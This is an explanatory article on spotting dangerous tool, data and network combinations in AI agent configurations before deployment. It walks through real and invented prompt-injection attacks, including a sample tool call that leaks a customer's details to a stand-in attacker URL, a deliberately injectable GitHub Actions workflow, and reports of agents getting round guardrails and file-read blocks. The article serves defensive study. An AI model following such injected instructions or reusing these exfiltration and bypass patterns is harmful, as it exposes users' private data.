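# Checking AI agent configurations for dangerous capability combinations before deployment

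## AI agents, their settings and the data theft a check should prevent

An AI agent is a language model that chooses and calls tools in a loop to carry out a task. Companies use agents to answer customers, repair software and search internal records, and often give each agent its own access keys. An agent's abilities depend on its configuration, the files and settings that determine its tools, credentials, permissions and network access before it runs. Some combinations of abilities let an outsider steal data through the agent, even when each tool is harmless alone. Configuration checking means looking for those combinations in the settings before the agent is deployed.

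For years, people used the word "agent" without agreeing on what it meant. At a developer conference in May 2025, Hannah Moran of Anthropic defined agents as "models using tools in a loop". The programmer Simon Willison (2025) welcomed the definition because speakers at the event had used the word dozens of times without defining it. He had collected 211 definitions from people on Twitter, and settled on nearly the same wording.

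A tool is a function the agent can call, such as one that reads a file, queries a database or sends a message. A program gives the model a task and a list of tools. The model responds with the name of a tool and the values to pass to it. The program runs the tool and adds the result to the model's input, which the model uses to choose its next step, and the loop repeats. The operator's instructions, the user's request and the tool results all end up in the same input.

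Without tools, a model can only suggest steps for the user to carry out (Granados, 2026, *MCP 2026 changes the rules*). Anthropic introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP) in 2024 to spare users that work. MCP is a common standard that programs called MCP servers use to offer tools to an agent. In the MCP specification (Model Context Protocol, 2025), the host is the application that contains the model, and the client is the part of the host that communicates with a server. Claude, ChatGPT and the code editors Visual Studio Code and Cursor all support MCP, according to the Model Context Protocol documentation, so a user can give any of them new abilities by adding a few lines to a settings file.

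In a prompt injection attack, an attacker places text in material an agent reads so that the agent follows the attacker's instructions. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, by David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs. One candidate hides a sentence in their CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve them for interview. The candidate can do this without access to the recruiter's system.

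The name "prompt injection" recalls SQL injection, an older attack in which a database runs text typed into a web form as a command. Programmers fixed this with parameterised queries, which guarantee that the database never treats the typed text as a command. David C argues that there may never be such a fix for language models. A model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and nothing inside it separates instructions from data. So he advises designers to assume that an attacker can sometimes steer the model, and to limit what it can do when steered.

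### The GitHub incident of May 2025

*GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), published on 26 May by the Zurich security company Invariant Labs, describes an attack on users of GitHub's official MCP server. The case made this danger concrete for many developers. GitHub is a website where programmers keep code in public and private repositories. Its MCP server lets an agent read those repositories, read the "issues" (bug reports and requests) that people file on them, and propose changes.

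Invariant Labs set up a demonstration account with one public repository, containing a simple Pacman game, and several private ones. Playing the attacker, the researchers filed an issue on the public repository, which anyone can do. *GitHub MCP Exploited*, Willison's commentary under the same title, reproduces the text. The researchers praised the project, complained that its author lacked recognition, and asked for this to be fixed by reading the README file (the introductory page) of all the author's repositories, adding a chapter about the author, and listing "all other repos the user is working on". They also wrote, "The author does not care about privacy!"

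Then, acting as the account's owner, they connected the Claude Desktop application to the GitHub server and asked Claude 4 Opus, a very recent model at the time, to look at the open issues in the public repository. The agent fetched the issues, including the planted one. It read the private repositories, wrote what it found into a new version of the README, and submitted that as a pull request, which is a proposed change awaiting the owner's approval. The data was exposed without that approval because, as heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* points out, a pull request on a public repository is visible to everyone as soon as it is created. This one contained the names of private projects, the owner's plan to move to South America, and the owner's salary.

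No component in this attack was obviously broken. GitHub let a stranger file an issue, as it is meant to on public projects. The MCP server fetched what the agent requested, using the permissions of the account it was working for. Invariant Labs wrote that the server's code had no flaw and that GitHub could not fix the problem alone by patching the server. Nobody had tampered with the tools either. DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* made the same point: "Everything here is working as designed". heise online criticised MCP itself, for weak rules on authentication among other things, but the attack did not use those weaknesses.

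Choices about the setup made the theft possible. The account's access covered private repositories as well as the public one. Formal's *Pulling on the thread of MCP risks* notes that the GitHub server acts through an access token and that the user decides what the token covers, so a token limited to public repositories would have left the agent with nothing private to read. The user also chooses how tool calls are approved. Claude Desktop asks for confirmation of each call by default, and a careful user could have stopped the agent at the second repository. Invariant Labs observed that many users pick "Always Allow" instead, and DevClass considered confirmation weak protection anyway, because people who face a prompt for every action stop reading the details. Willison noted that a single server supplied all three parts of what he calls the lethal trifecta, namely private data, malicious instructions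 and a way to send information out.

This was a demonstration on an account built for the purpose, with no real victim. Invariant Labs also sells security tools for agents and promoted them in the same article. Neither fact affects the mechanism, which anyone could follow in the published record of the session.

### Could a better model solve the problem?

One could argue that the model was at fault for obeying a stranger, and that a model that refuses would make settings matter much less. Developers have made progress on this. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports a test by the security company Gray Swan in which attackers got up to 15 attempts per scenario. They succeeded in an estimated 8.5% of scenarios against GPT-6 Astra, down from 27.0% against the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 did better still. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt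 injection* reports that attackers had a 2.0% success rate after 15 attempts in a Gray Swan test and no successes in 129 scenarios with a web-browsing agent.

Attacks succeeded against the same Opus 5 in 10.0% of cases in PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark built from long office tasks such as analysing a bond portfolio. The rate was 2.4% for the best model, Gemini 4 Carbon, and averaged 34.9% over the first 21 models. PromptArmor is a security vendor and designed its attacks to beat current models, so its figures are probably on the high side. Still, a range from zero to 10% for one model suggests that the rate depends on the attack and the task as much as on the model. A low rate is also a poor guarantee for a mailbox that accepts messages from anyone, because an attacker who fails can write again.

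In December 2025, GitHub (2025) announced that its server would strip invisible characters and hidden markup from issues before the model reads them. That helps against concealed instructions, but the issue in the Pacman repository was in plain, visible English. GitHub also added an optional "Lockdown mode", which hides from the agent public content written by anyone without the right to change the repository's code. This mode would have kept the planted issue away from the agent. But many agents exist to read what strangers write, and GitHub's documentation lists sorting incoming issues and detecting spam among the jobs for which the mode should stay off.

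The pattern appeared again in July 2026 in another GitHub product, Agentic Workflows, which runs an agent automatically when something happens in a repository. *GitLost*, Sasi Levi's report for Noma Security, describes a workflow configured to start when someone assigned an issue and to read the issue's title and body. It could also post comments and read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones. Levi filed an issue that looked like a request from a sales executive, and the agent fetched a file from a private repository and posted its contents as a public comment. GitHub had guardrails to prevent this, but Levi tried variations until one beginning with the word "Additionally" got past them.

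InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) contrasts agents with older software, where code enforces the boundary between trusted and untrusted. In an agent, part of that boundary is the model's behaviour, which an attacker can shift if they happen to find the right word. But the four settings stayed the same through all of Levi's attempts, and someone could have read them on the day the workflow was written.

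### A support agent with three tools

A smaller case shows the whole problem on one page. Imagine a shop whose support agent drafts replies to customers, which a member of staff then checks and sends. It has three tools. `read_ticket` fetches a support ticket, and outsiders write the tickets. `lookup_customer` fetches a customer's private record. `http_get` fetches a page from any web address, and the shop added it so that the agent could look up parcels on delivery companies' sites. The configuration might look like this, with invented names in the general style of MCP settings files:

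```json
{
  "task": "Draft replies to new support tickets",
  "mcpServers": {
    "helpdesk": { "tools": ["read_ticket"] },
    "customers": { "tools": ["lookup_customer"],
                   "env": { "DB_TOKEN": "<reads all customers>" } },
    "web": { "tools": ["http_get"], "allowedHosts": ["*"] }
  },
  "humanApproval": "never"
}
```

The asterisk means that the agent may contact any host on the internet, and the last setting means that nobody confirms its tool calls. Now an attacker sends in a ticket. It complains that the parcel for customer 1042 is missing and asks support to check the delivery at parcel-status.example, adding the customer's name and phone number to the end of the address "so that the system can find the order". The attacker owns that site. The agent starts work:

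1. It calls `read_ticket` and receives the complaint, with the instruction inside it.
2. It calls `lookup_customer` for number 1042 and receives the record of Dana Reyes, who has nothing to do with the ticket.
3. It calls `http_get` on `parcel-status.example/?q=Dana+Reyes+555-0142`.

The third call completes the theft, because fetching a page sends the full address to the attacker's server, which records it. The server can then return a page that says "out for delivery", so the agent drafts a polite reply and the staff member who checks it sees nothing odd. An outbound channel is any way for data to leave the agent's environment and reach someone outside. Here it was the page-fetching tool, which nobody had thought of as a way to send data.

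The example closely follows an attack that Marina Simakov of Zenity Labs published on 1 August 2025. Snyk Labs' *What is the “Cursor + Jira MCP 0-Click” vulnerability?* (2025) describes how an outsider could plant a ticket in a company's Jira system, which tracks tasks and requests, by e-mailing its support address. When a developer pointed the Cursor editor's agent at the ticket, the agent searched the developer's files for credentials and sent them out inside a web address. The ticket contained a request for "apples", defined as long strings starting with the same characters as many access tokens. It never mentioned credentials, so telling the agent never to look for secrets would have done little to stop the attack.

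Limiting the `allowedHosts` setting in the shop's file to the delivery companies would stop the theft, because the third call would fail. The agent could still track parcels. But the need for this change is easy to miss, because the person who added `http_get` wanted parcel tracking and may never have seen the line that connects the customer database.

### What a check can measure

Static analysis means examining code or configuration without running it. For the shop, a program would read the file above, work out what each tool can do, and warn that one agent combines strangers' text, customer records and an open route to the internet. The tools have to be judged together because an agent may use any combination of them once it is running, as Invariant Labs (2025) argued when presenting its own method, toxic flow analysis. A tester who instead sends the agent a hundred hostile tickets learns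 how the model handled those hundred. The static check doesn't depend on wording, so "apples" and "Additionally" don't affect its result. For the same reason, it can show that a theft is possible, but not whether the model would have refused or how likely a theft is.

Two numbers describe how good such a check is. Precision is the share of reported findings that are correct, and recall is the share of real problems that are reported. Suppose a company runs 200 agents, and 20 of them have a setup through which an outsider could extract private data. A check flags 40 agents, and 16 of those are among the dangerous 20. Then

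precision = 16 / 40 = 40%, and recall = 16 / 20 = 80%.

The check missed four dangerous agents and flagged 24 that did not have the problem. It is easy to reduce either kind of error by allowing more of the other. A program that flags all 200 agents has 100% recall but only 10% precision. If it flags only the most obvious case, it may reach 100% precision but miss the other 19 dangerous agents. Recall and precision also depend on what counts as a real problem. If the shop's model would resist 98 out of 100 hostile tickets, its owners may call the warning a false alarm, while a security team that expects thousands of tickets would call it correct.

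The questions are therefore whether a program can reliably flag a setup like the shop's from its configuration, and whether the people who receive the flag will act on it when the last few they looked into were false alarms.

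## Which combinations of capabilities are hazardous

A program can flag a setup like the shop's only if someone has defined what makes it dangerous. Willison offered a definition in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (16 June 2025), which warned users against combining three things in one agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. He meant all three broadly. An agent is exposed to untrusted content if text or images under an attacker's control can reach the model in any way. Communication counts if it "could be used to steal your data", whatever the tool is for, so a tool that loads an image or shows the user a link to click qualifies.

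Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) followed on 31 October. Meta took the idea partly from Willison and partly from a guideline for Chromium browser programmers. That guideline, which Willison noted dates from 2019, allows code to combine at most two of untrustworthy inputs, an unsafe programming language and high privilege. Meta's rule similarly allows an agent at most two of three properties within a session, which lasts until the model starts again with a fresh context window (the text it works from).

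| | Lethal trifecta | Rule of Two |
|---|---|---|
| What comes in | Text or images an attacker could control | [A] Untrustworthy inputs |
| What the agent can reach | Private data | [B] Sensitive systems or private data |
| What the agent can do | Communicate externally in a way that could carry data | [C] Change state or communicate externally |
| Advice | Never combine all three | Combine all three only under supervision |

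Changing state means altering something that lasts, such as a file, a customer record or a bank balance. Supervision means that a person or some other reliable check approves the agent's actions. People are not very reliable supervisors. Willison reports that in a study Anthropic published in August 2026, only 13.6% of 1,053 paid developers refused a clearly dangerous command that the organisers had swapped into one of their permission prompts.

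Meta gives the example of an e-mail assistant that receives a spam message with instructions to collect the contents of the inbox and forward them to a stranger. The developer can prevent this by letting the assistant read only mail from trusted senders, by denying it access to real data, or by letting it write only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft. Without real data, the assistant cannot read anyone's e-mail, so the second option is useful mainly for testing.

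Meta counts properties per session, so the order of an agent's actions can matter. An agent could browse the web first and then permanently lose its outbound channel before it opens any internal system. Meta's wording leaves some doubt about whether "change state" includes the agent's own saved notes, which a later session might read. McKerchar's article for the security company Sophos, *Inside the lethal trifecta*, paraphrases the property as changing state "externally", which would exclude such notes.

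### From three conditions to a theft

Willison's argument has four steps:

1. Models do not reliably separate instructions from data.
2. An agent that follows an attacker's instructions can use every tool it holds.
3. So an agent that meets all three conditions can fetch private data and send it to the attacker.
4. This kind of theft needs all three conditions, so removing one prevents it.

The second step follows because the program that runs the model's tool calls doesn't record whose instructions led to each call. In the shop, `lookup_customer` works the same way for the staff and for the author of a hostile ticket. Some products now check calls before running them. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, has an "auto mode" in which a separate classifier blocks calls that look dangerous. The attacker can then use only the calls that the classifier lets through.

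The fourth step is the most reliable because it does not depend on the model. Without hostile text, no attacker is steering the agent; without private data, there is nothing to steal; and without a channel for sending data out, the data stays where it is. But it can be hard to tell whether one of these conditions is really absent.

The remaining claim, about models, is the most disputed, and all the others depend on it. mbgsec's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), a commentary on Meta's post, welcomed Meta's statement that prompt injection is unsolved and complained that some people at Anthropic and OpenAI still thought it could be fixed. According to The Decoder, OpenAI conceded in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved. By August 2026 Anthropic was much more optimistic. Thariq Shihipar, who works on Claude Code, said of the company's latest results that "we should have called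 this post 'defeating the lethal trifecta'".

### How often injection succeeds

Anthropic's system card for Claude Fable 5.1, dated 1 September 2026, contains some of the lowest attack success rates any developer has reported. They come from Gray Swan, which collected 1,804 attacks from public competitions, choosing ones that worked against several models. The attacks cover 37 scenarios in coding, tool use and operating a computer through its screen. The attacker's aims include stealing data, destroying it and moving money. The table gives the probability that at least one attempt succeeds.

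| Model | 1 attempt | 10 attempts | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 0.7% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 3.6% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 4.9% | 6.5% |

Models have become much better at resisting prompt injection. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reported on an earlier Gray Swan test in which attackers given ten attempts succeeded against that model 33.6% of the time. The two tests used different attacks, so the figures are only roughly comparable, but a fall from 33.6% to 0.7% is too large to dismiss.

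The 1.0% probably understates what a determined attacker could do. Attackers tailor their attacks to the model in front of them, so Anthropic reports results only for models that the competitions had not targeted. The attackers had therefore practised on other models, whereas a thief who wanted to break into a Fable 5.1 agent would practise on Fable 5.1. New attacks can also raise the rate. Opus 5's rate after 15 attempts rose from 2.0% at its release to 4.8% in the September card, for which Anthropic had added nine scenarios and 670 attacks. On the other hand, Gray Swan tested the Claude models without the extra defences against injection that Anthropic runs in many of its products.

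An older experiment shows how much more effective adaptive attacks can be than fixed ones. Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, describes *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 paper by 14 researchers, some of them from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. They tested 12 published defences, most of which had originally reported near-zero attack success rates, against attacks that adapted over many rounds. Most of the defences failed more than 90% of the time. One of them, PIGuard, stopped every fixed attack but let through 71% of the automated adaptive ones. In a competition with 500 participants and a $20,000 prize fund, people defeated all 12. Today's models do not use these defences, so the percentages do not carry over, but defences still need to be tested against adaptive attacks.

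OpenAI's figures for GPT-6 Astra show a similar gap. In the company's internal test, the model resisted 99.79% of indirect injections, which are hidden in other people's content. If attempts were independent, a 0.21% failure rate would give an attacker about a 3% chance of success within 15 tries, well below the 8.5% that Gray Swan's attacks reached. The two tests differ in both tasks and attackers. OpenAI's test relies on GPT-Red, an automated attacker that the company also uses in training, so the model may well have learned to resist GPT-Red's methods in particular.

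The best result for the defence, and the one Shihipar was talking about, comes from a test that Anthropic commissioned. Trajectory Labs attacked Claude Code in auto mode, using 72 scenarios that Anthropic had not seen. None of 720 attempts succeeded against Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5. By the usual statistical rule of thumb, this is still compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.4% per attempt, and it applies only to attacks like those in the test. Willison wrote that he would love to believe the problem was solved but wanted more independent confirmation. He suggested an attack that he thought would get through, in which a software package's instructions ask the agent to download "model files" before running the package's tests, using a command that actually steals data. The request would look routine, since programmers' agents often install software.

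### The attacker who tries again

Willison's usual reply to figures like these is that "In application security, 99% is a failing grade." He argues that if one attack in a hundred works, an attacker will find it. He was responding to an article in The Economist that recommended treating AI the way Victorian engineers treated iron. They could not trust the material, so they built bridges much stronger than necessary. Willison thinks this approach is wrong for security. Attackers deliberately search for weak points, whereas flaws in iron occur by chance.

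The arithmetic seems to support him. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, independently of the others, then the chance of at least one success in n attempts is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

For p = 1%, that comes to 63% after 100 attempts and 95% after 300.

Real attempts are not independent, however, and measured success rates rise more slowly than the formula predicts. The Decoder reports that a single strong attack on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time. At that rate, the formula predicts a 99% chance of at least one success in 100 attempts, but the measured figure was 63%. Attacks seem to fail almost always on some tasks and succeed quickly on others. VentureBeat found the same split in the February 2026 system card for Claude Opus 4.6. In a restricted coding environment, none of 200 attempts succeeded. When the model operated a computer through its graphical interface without safeguards,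 a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and at least one of 200 attempts succeeded 78.6% of the time. With safeguards, the 200-attempt figure was 57.1%.

Persistence therefore does not guarantee that an attacker will break into any particular agent, and "99% is a failing grade" is a little too strong for a company with one agent doing one narrow job. But attackers rarely need a particular agent. Anthropic points out that someone can send the same e-mail to a thousand inboxes and, if the attack works, compromise every agent that summarises it. An average success rate of 0.1% across many attacks does not protect the people who receive the one that works. At the end of 2026, models still do not *reliably* separate instructions from data, although they fail much less often than they did in 2025.

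### One tool, several conditions

In the shop, each tool supplied one condition, but often one tool supplies all of them. A shell tool lets an agent run any command on a computer. The agent can use `curl` to download a page that an attacker wrote, `cat` to print a file of passwords, and `curl` again to send them away. A settings file that lists only this tool looks modest, but the agent meets the full definition. The conditions a tool supplies depend on what it can reach. In a sealed environment with no network and no secrets, the same tool supplies at most the untrusted content, and only if someone gives it a stranger's files to work on.

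A shell can also let an agent bypass limits on its other tools. In November 2025, Willison described an attack by PromptArmor on Antigravity, Google's code editor. The researchers hid instructions in tiny type on a web page that posed as a technical guide. The editor correctly blocked its file-reading tools from opening the file that held the access keys. The reasoning output of the model, Gemini, mentioned the block and a plan to print the file with a shell command instead. The next step in the attack was to send the keys out through the browser tool, whose default list of permitted sites included one where anyone can record incoming requests.

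Some MCP servers combine the conditions in a less obvious way. The server for Supabase, a database service, let an agent read support messages from customers, read a table of access tokens, and write to the database. Researchers at General Analysis showed that a hostile message could make the agent copy the tokens into a reply on the same ticket, where the attacker could read them. The agent leaked the tokens through an ordinary database write, without sending an e-mail or web request.

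An agent that can write to a public repository can also publish anything it knows, even if no tool on its list has "send" in its name. This happened to the owner of the Pacman game. The risk depends on who can read what the agent writes. If only employees can read the repository, the write is internal and the trifecta is incomplete, unless someone later makes the repository public. A checker can't distinguish public from internal writes by tool name alone, because a tool for creating pull requests has the same name in both cases.

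Fetching a web page is the hardest of these cases to judge, because developers have tried to make it safe. The shop's `http_get` accepts any address the model composes, but Claude's own fetching tool in the chat application could open only addresses that the user had typed or that came from a search, plus links on pages it had already opened. Ayush Paul's attack, which Willison described in July 2026, needed only those links. Paul built a site that supposedly held user profiles in alphabetical order, with one link for each letter, and asked the agent to navigate to its user's profile. The agent spelled out the user's name by following links, and the server recorded each one.

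Each click reveals one of 26 letters, or about 4.7 bits of information, so leaking a ten-letter name takes ten clicks. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer this way. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links it finds on fetched pages. A checker that relied on the old rule ("the model cannot construct addresses") could reasonably have concluded that there was no outbound channel, although a slow one existed.

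### Harm without theft

Suppose the shop replaces `lookup_customer` and `http_get` with a tool that permanently deletes tickets, so that the agent can clear out duplicates. An attacker submits a ticket claiming that the last 500 tickets are copies of it. The agent deletes them, and the shop loses 500 complaints even though no private data leaked and the trifecta was never complete.

The main objection to the trifecta is that it is too narrow, because it covers who can see data but not damage to the data itself. Willison agrees. He wrote that prompt injection causes "even nastier" harms than theft, and he liked the Rule of Two a lot because it adds changing state to the list. He later objected that Meta's diagram marked every pair of properties as "safe", including untrusted input together with the ability to change state. He argued that this pair can do harm even without private data or sensitive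 systems, and that making an exception for it would complicate a simple rule.

Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that "sensitive systems" covers any system that matters to the user's security, whether or not it holds secrets. An agent without access to such systems can change things freely only because it works somewhere harmless, such as a sealed test environment. Meta also changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk".

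The rule still covers this case if, as Ayzenberg reads it, the shop's ticket system counts as a sensitive system. The deletion tool then supplies two of the three properties, access to a sensitive system and the power to change state, and a ticket from a stranger supplies the third. A checker can more simply treat the hazard as untrusted content combined with an irreversible action on an important system. Such actions include deleting records without a backup and making a payment, but not adding a tag to a ticket, because staff can remove it. Without the limit to irreversible actions, the rule would flag nearly every agent that does any work.

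Willison's objection still partly holds. Meta describes a research assistant that may fill in forms on any website, and makes it acceptable by running its browser without the user's accounts or data. A hostile page could still make the assistant post spam across the internet, which other people would have to clean up, though the user would lose nothing. Meta acknowledges that the rule does not address spam or an agent's own mistakes.

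An agent can also leak data by mistake. OpenAI tested GPT-6 Astra on office tasks with ambiguous instructions and complicated permissions. The model leaked data in 4.5% of the tasks, even with a policy on when to ask for approval. The tasks were deliberately difficult, so the rate in ordinary work should be lower. But this kind of leak requires only private data and an outbound channel, and neither the trifecta nor the Rule of Two would prevent it.

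### When most useful agents qualify

Bowley, by contrast, argues in *Does the “lethal trifecta” kill the idea of fully autonomous AI Agents* that people do not yet appreciate how severely the three conditions restrict what agents can be used for. McKerchar of Sophos writes that the agents companies already run often meet all three. Sophos sells security products and so has an interest in saying this, but the claim is easy to believe, because an assistant that answers e-mail has to read strangers' messages, know its owner's business and send replies. Meta admits that its rule does not suit some popular uses, such as agents that run in the background, where stopping to ask a person is disruptive or pointless.

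OpenAI's behaviour suggests that developers accept the combination knowingly. In June 2026 the company began offering ChatGPT users a "Lockdown Mode", which limits outbound requests to make it harder to extract data through a successful prompt injection. Willison praised it, but inferred from its existence that the default settings offer no robust protection against a determined thief. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's security chief, said the mode was for people at higher risk and "not meant for everyone", because it removes some functionality.

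The definition still holds, since a useful agent can also be vulnerable to data theft, but used alone it doesn't help a security team set priorities. If 150 of a company's 200 agents meet all three conditions, the team gets 150 warnings and no idea where to start. One of those agents may read mail from anyone and have access to the payroll, while another may read documents from two known suppliers and have access to no private data except an unpublished lunch menu. To tell them apart, a checker has to find out whose text each agent reads, which data it can reach and where its messages can go.

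## What configuration files reveal about an agent and what they leave out

The shop's agent fits in one short file only because it is invented. A real agent's tools may be in one file and its keys in another, while a different team manages the limits on its network traffic in a cloud account. A given file can show that a condition of the trifecta is present, show that it is absent, or leave it undetermined. A checker that treats undetermined conditions as absent will pass dangerous agents.

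| Artefact | Untrusted content | Private data | Outbound channel |
|---|---|---|---|
| MCP server list | Hinted at by server names | A credential exists, but its reach is open | Hinted at by server names |
| Coding-agent permission settings | Whether the agent may fetch web pages | Which folders it may read | Which commands run without approval |
| Environment variables | Left open | Names of the keys present | Left open |
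| Framework code | Where outside text enters, if the code is simple | Which data functions the agent holds | Which sending functions it holds |
| Continuous-integration workflow | Established by the trigger and the prompt | Names of secrets, permissions of the built-in token | Established by write permissions |
| Cloud role | Left open | Which stored data the role may read | Which cloud services it may write to |
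| Network rules | Which sites it can read from | Which internal systems it can contact | Established or ruled out, if something enforces the rules |

An MCP server list gives the command or web address for each server, often with a credential. Coding agents such as Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex also have permission settings, which determine what they may do without asking. An environment variable is a named value that the operating system passes to a program when it starts, and programmers often store access keys there. Framework code assembles an agent and attaches its tools, but recovering the agent's structure from that code is a separate problem. A continuous-integration workflow lists jobs that run automatically when code changes or another event occurs in a repository. A cloud role is a set of permissions that a cloud provider attaches to a program.

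The outbound channel is the easiest condition to rule out. If the network rules permit only two delivery companies' sites, it hardly matters which tools the agent has. Private data is harder to rule out, because most files name a key without describing what it gives access to. Untrusted content may be the hardest, since a tool called `read_ticket` has the same name whether customers or only employees write the tickets.

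### Workflows that declare nearly everything

The checker's job is easiest when an agent runs inside GitHub Actions, GitHub's service for continuous-integration workflows. Suppose the shop keeps its website's code in a public repository and wants an agent to answer bug reports that mention an order. The action (a reusable component) in this workflow is invented:

```yaml
on:
  issues:
    types: [opened]
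permissions:
  contents: read
  issues: write
jobs:
  answer:
    runs-on: ubuntu-latest
    steps:
      - id: agent
        uses: example/agent-action@v1
        with:
          allow-users: "*"
          prompt: |
            Look up the order in this report and draft an answer.
            ${{ github.event.issue.body }}
        env:
          ORDERS_KEY: ${{ secrets.ORDERS_KEY }}
      - run: gh issue comment "$NUMBER" --body "$ANSWER"
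        env:
          NUMBER: ${{ github.event.issue.number }}
          ANSWER: ${{ steps.agent.outputs.answer }}
          GH_TOKEN: ${{ github.token }}
```

The workflow runs when someone files a new issue, which anyone can do on a public repository, and the issue's text goes straight into the prompt. The agent has a key to the order system, and the last step publishes its answer as a comment. The agent also has a second outbound channel because the file doesn't restrict network access, which GitHub describes as unrestricted by default in ordinary Actions workflows. The file doesn't show whether the repository is public or what `ORDERS_KEY` can read.

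In *Demystifying and Detecting Agentic Workflow Injection Vulnerabilities in GitHub Actions*, Wang, Hou and colleagues (2026) ran a scanner they built, TaintAWI, on 13,392 workflows that use AI actions. The scanner needs a record of what each action does, so they first used a language model to classify 1,033 actions from their descriptions and documentation. For each one, it recorded whether the action's own model gets tools, which inputs become part of the prompt, which outputs that model writes, and whether the action restricts who may start it. These records agreed with human labels on 95.9% of the fields in a sample of 100, and people reviewed the most widely used actions in full. Of the 1,033 actions, 453 accept a prompt, but only 21 restrict who may start them.

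TaintAWI then applies taint analysis, a method that marks data from outsiders as "tainted" and follows it through a program. It converts each workflow into a graph whose edges show where data can flow between steps, jobs and scripts, and applies five rules:

1. Mark every value an outsider controls, such as an issue's title or body, as tainted.
2. If a tainted value can flow into another value, mark that one too.
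3. If a tainted value reaches the prompt of an action whose model has tools, report a *prompt-to-agent* problem.
4. If a tainted value reaches the prompt of any AI action, mark everything the model writes as tainted.
5. If tainted model output reaches a command that changes something, report a *prompt-to-script* problem.

The fourth rule is a deliberate overestimate. No one can tell from the file whether a hostile issue will change the model's answer, so the scanner assumes it will. In the shop's workflow, the third rule fires on the prompt and the fifth on the comment. OpenAI's repository for Codex had both problems in a workflow that chose labels for new issues, and OpenAI acknowledged the report.

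Before reporting a workflow, the scanner checks for guards, such as a condition that only maintainers may start the job. A list of permitted users counts as a guard unless it is set to "everyone", as it is in the shop's file. A sentence in the prompt telling the model to ignore injected instructions never counts, because it is part of the text the attacker is trying to override. Of 881 workflows with a tainted path, 362 had an effective guard, so the scanner would have raised 70% more alerts without this check.

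TaintAWI flagged 519 workflows, and the researchers confirmed 496 of them by hand, a precision of 95.6%. They had seen no earlier public reports of 343 of these. They also ran four other scanners on the same files.

| Scanner | Workflows reported | Confirmed cases included |
|---|---|---|
| TaintAWI | 519 | 496 |
| Argus | 831 | 66 |
| CodeQL | 1,486 | 76 |
| Aikido's OpenGrep rules | 1,658 | 73 |
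| Prompt Injection Scanner | 2,079 | 78 |

This comparison favours TaintAWI, because all the confirmed cases come from its own reports. None of the other tools follows data through a model's output, so they could not find prompt-to-script problems. On prompt-to-agent problems alone, TaintAWI's lead is much smaller, at 103 cases to 78 for the next best tool.

To estimate what TaintAWI had missed, Wang and colleagues sampled 100 alerts from each of the four rival tools, choosing only alerts that TaintAWI had not raised. Of these 400 alerts, 13 were real problems. In total, the rivals raised about 5,760 alerts that TaintAWI did not. If the same rate held for all of them, TaintAWI missed up to about 190 workflows, or fewer if more than one rival flagged the same workflow. Its recall would then be above 70%, counting only problems that at least one of the five tools can detect.

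The precision figure also calls for caution. The researchers graded their own tool, although 24 of the 26 maintainers who replied accepted or fixed the problem. The cases are far from independent, since 393 of the 496 involve a single action, `ai-inference`. In addition, 93 of the 519 reports were copies of one faulty template that GitHub had published and later corrected, so a scanner that classifies that template correctly is right 93 times. "Confirmed" means that a stranger's text can reach the agent or a later command, but the study does not measure how often a model would follow instructions in that text.

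TaintAWI does not look for the full trifecta either, because it has no category for private data. Most of its findings concern tampering. Of the confirmed cases, 391 let an outsider influence changes on GitHub, such as labels and comments, and only four involve sending data over the network. To find data theft, a checker would have to combine the paths TaintAWI finds with the secrets and permissions in the same file.

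The study recommends passing the agent only an issue's number and letting it fetch the text with a restricted command. This keeps strangers' words out of the maintainer's instructions, but the model still reads them. Following this advice would also make the untrusted content harder for the scanner to detect, because the scanner doesn't treat the number as a tainted source, so the path would disappear from its graph. A check for the trifecta would need to treat the fetching command itself as a source.

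### What GitHub checks at compile time

GitHub Agentic Workflows, the product that Sasi Levi attacked in July 2026, goes further than scanning by refusing to compile workflows whose settings break certain rules. The user writes a Markdown file with a settings block at the top and plain-English instructions below it, and a compiler turns the file into an ordinary Actions workflow if the settings are allowed. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) says the product's designers assume that an agent will try to read things it shouldn't and to misuse legitimate channels.

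According to GitHub's *Security Architecture*, the compiler verifies that every setting exists and has the right type. It permits only listed expressions, so an author cannot use an expression to insert a secret into the prompt. It ties each action to a fingerprint of one exact version, so the action's author cannot change the code later under the same version name. Three outside scanners, actionlint, zizmor and poutine, are optional. Strict mode, on by default, also forbids write permissions for the agent, requires explicit network settings and rejects wildcard domains, so the shop's `"allowedHosts": ["*"]` would not compile.

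Some of these checks cover combinations of settings. A workflow triggered by `pull_request_target` runs with the main repository's secrets, even when a stranger proposed the change. If the workflow also downloads and runs the stranger's code, the stranger can steal those secrets. GitHub's compiler warns about this trigger unless the workflow's author turns off the download, and in strict mode the warning becomes an error.

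The declared settings also closely match the effective ones, because other components enforce them at run time. A proxy outside the agent's container blocks every domain not on the list. The agent cannot write to GitHub. It describes a proposed comment or pull request, and a separate job with its own permissions checks the proposal and posts it.

Even so, a workflow like the one Levi exploited breaks none of these rules, because each setting is legitimate on its own and no rule covers the combination. According to the documentation, this gap exists partly because tokens are "imported capabilities", whose powers someone set elsewhere, so the compiler's plan cannot protect against a token that was given too much power when it was created.

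### What a token can reach

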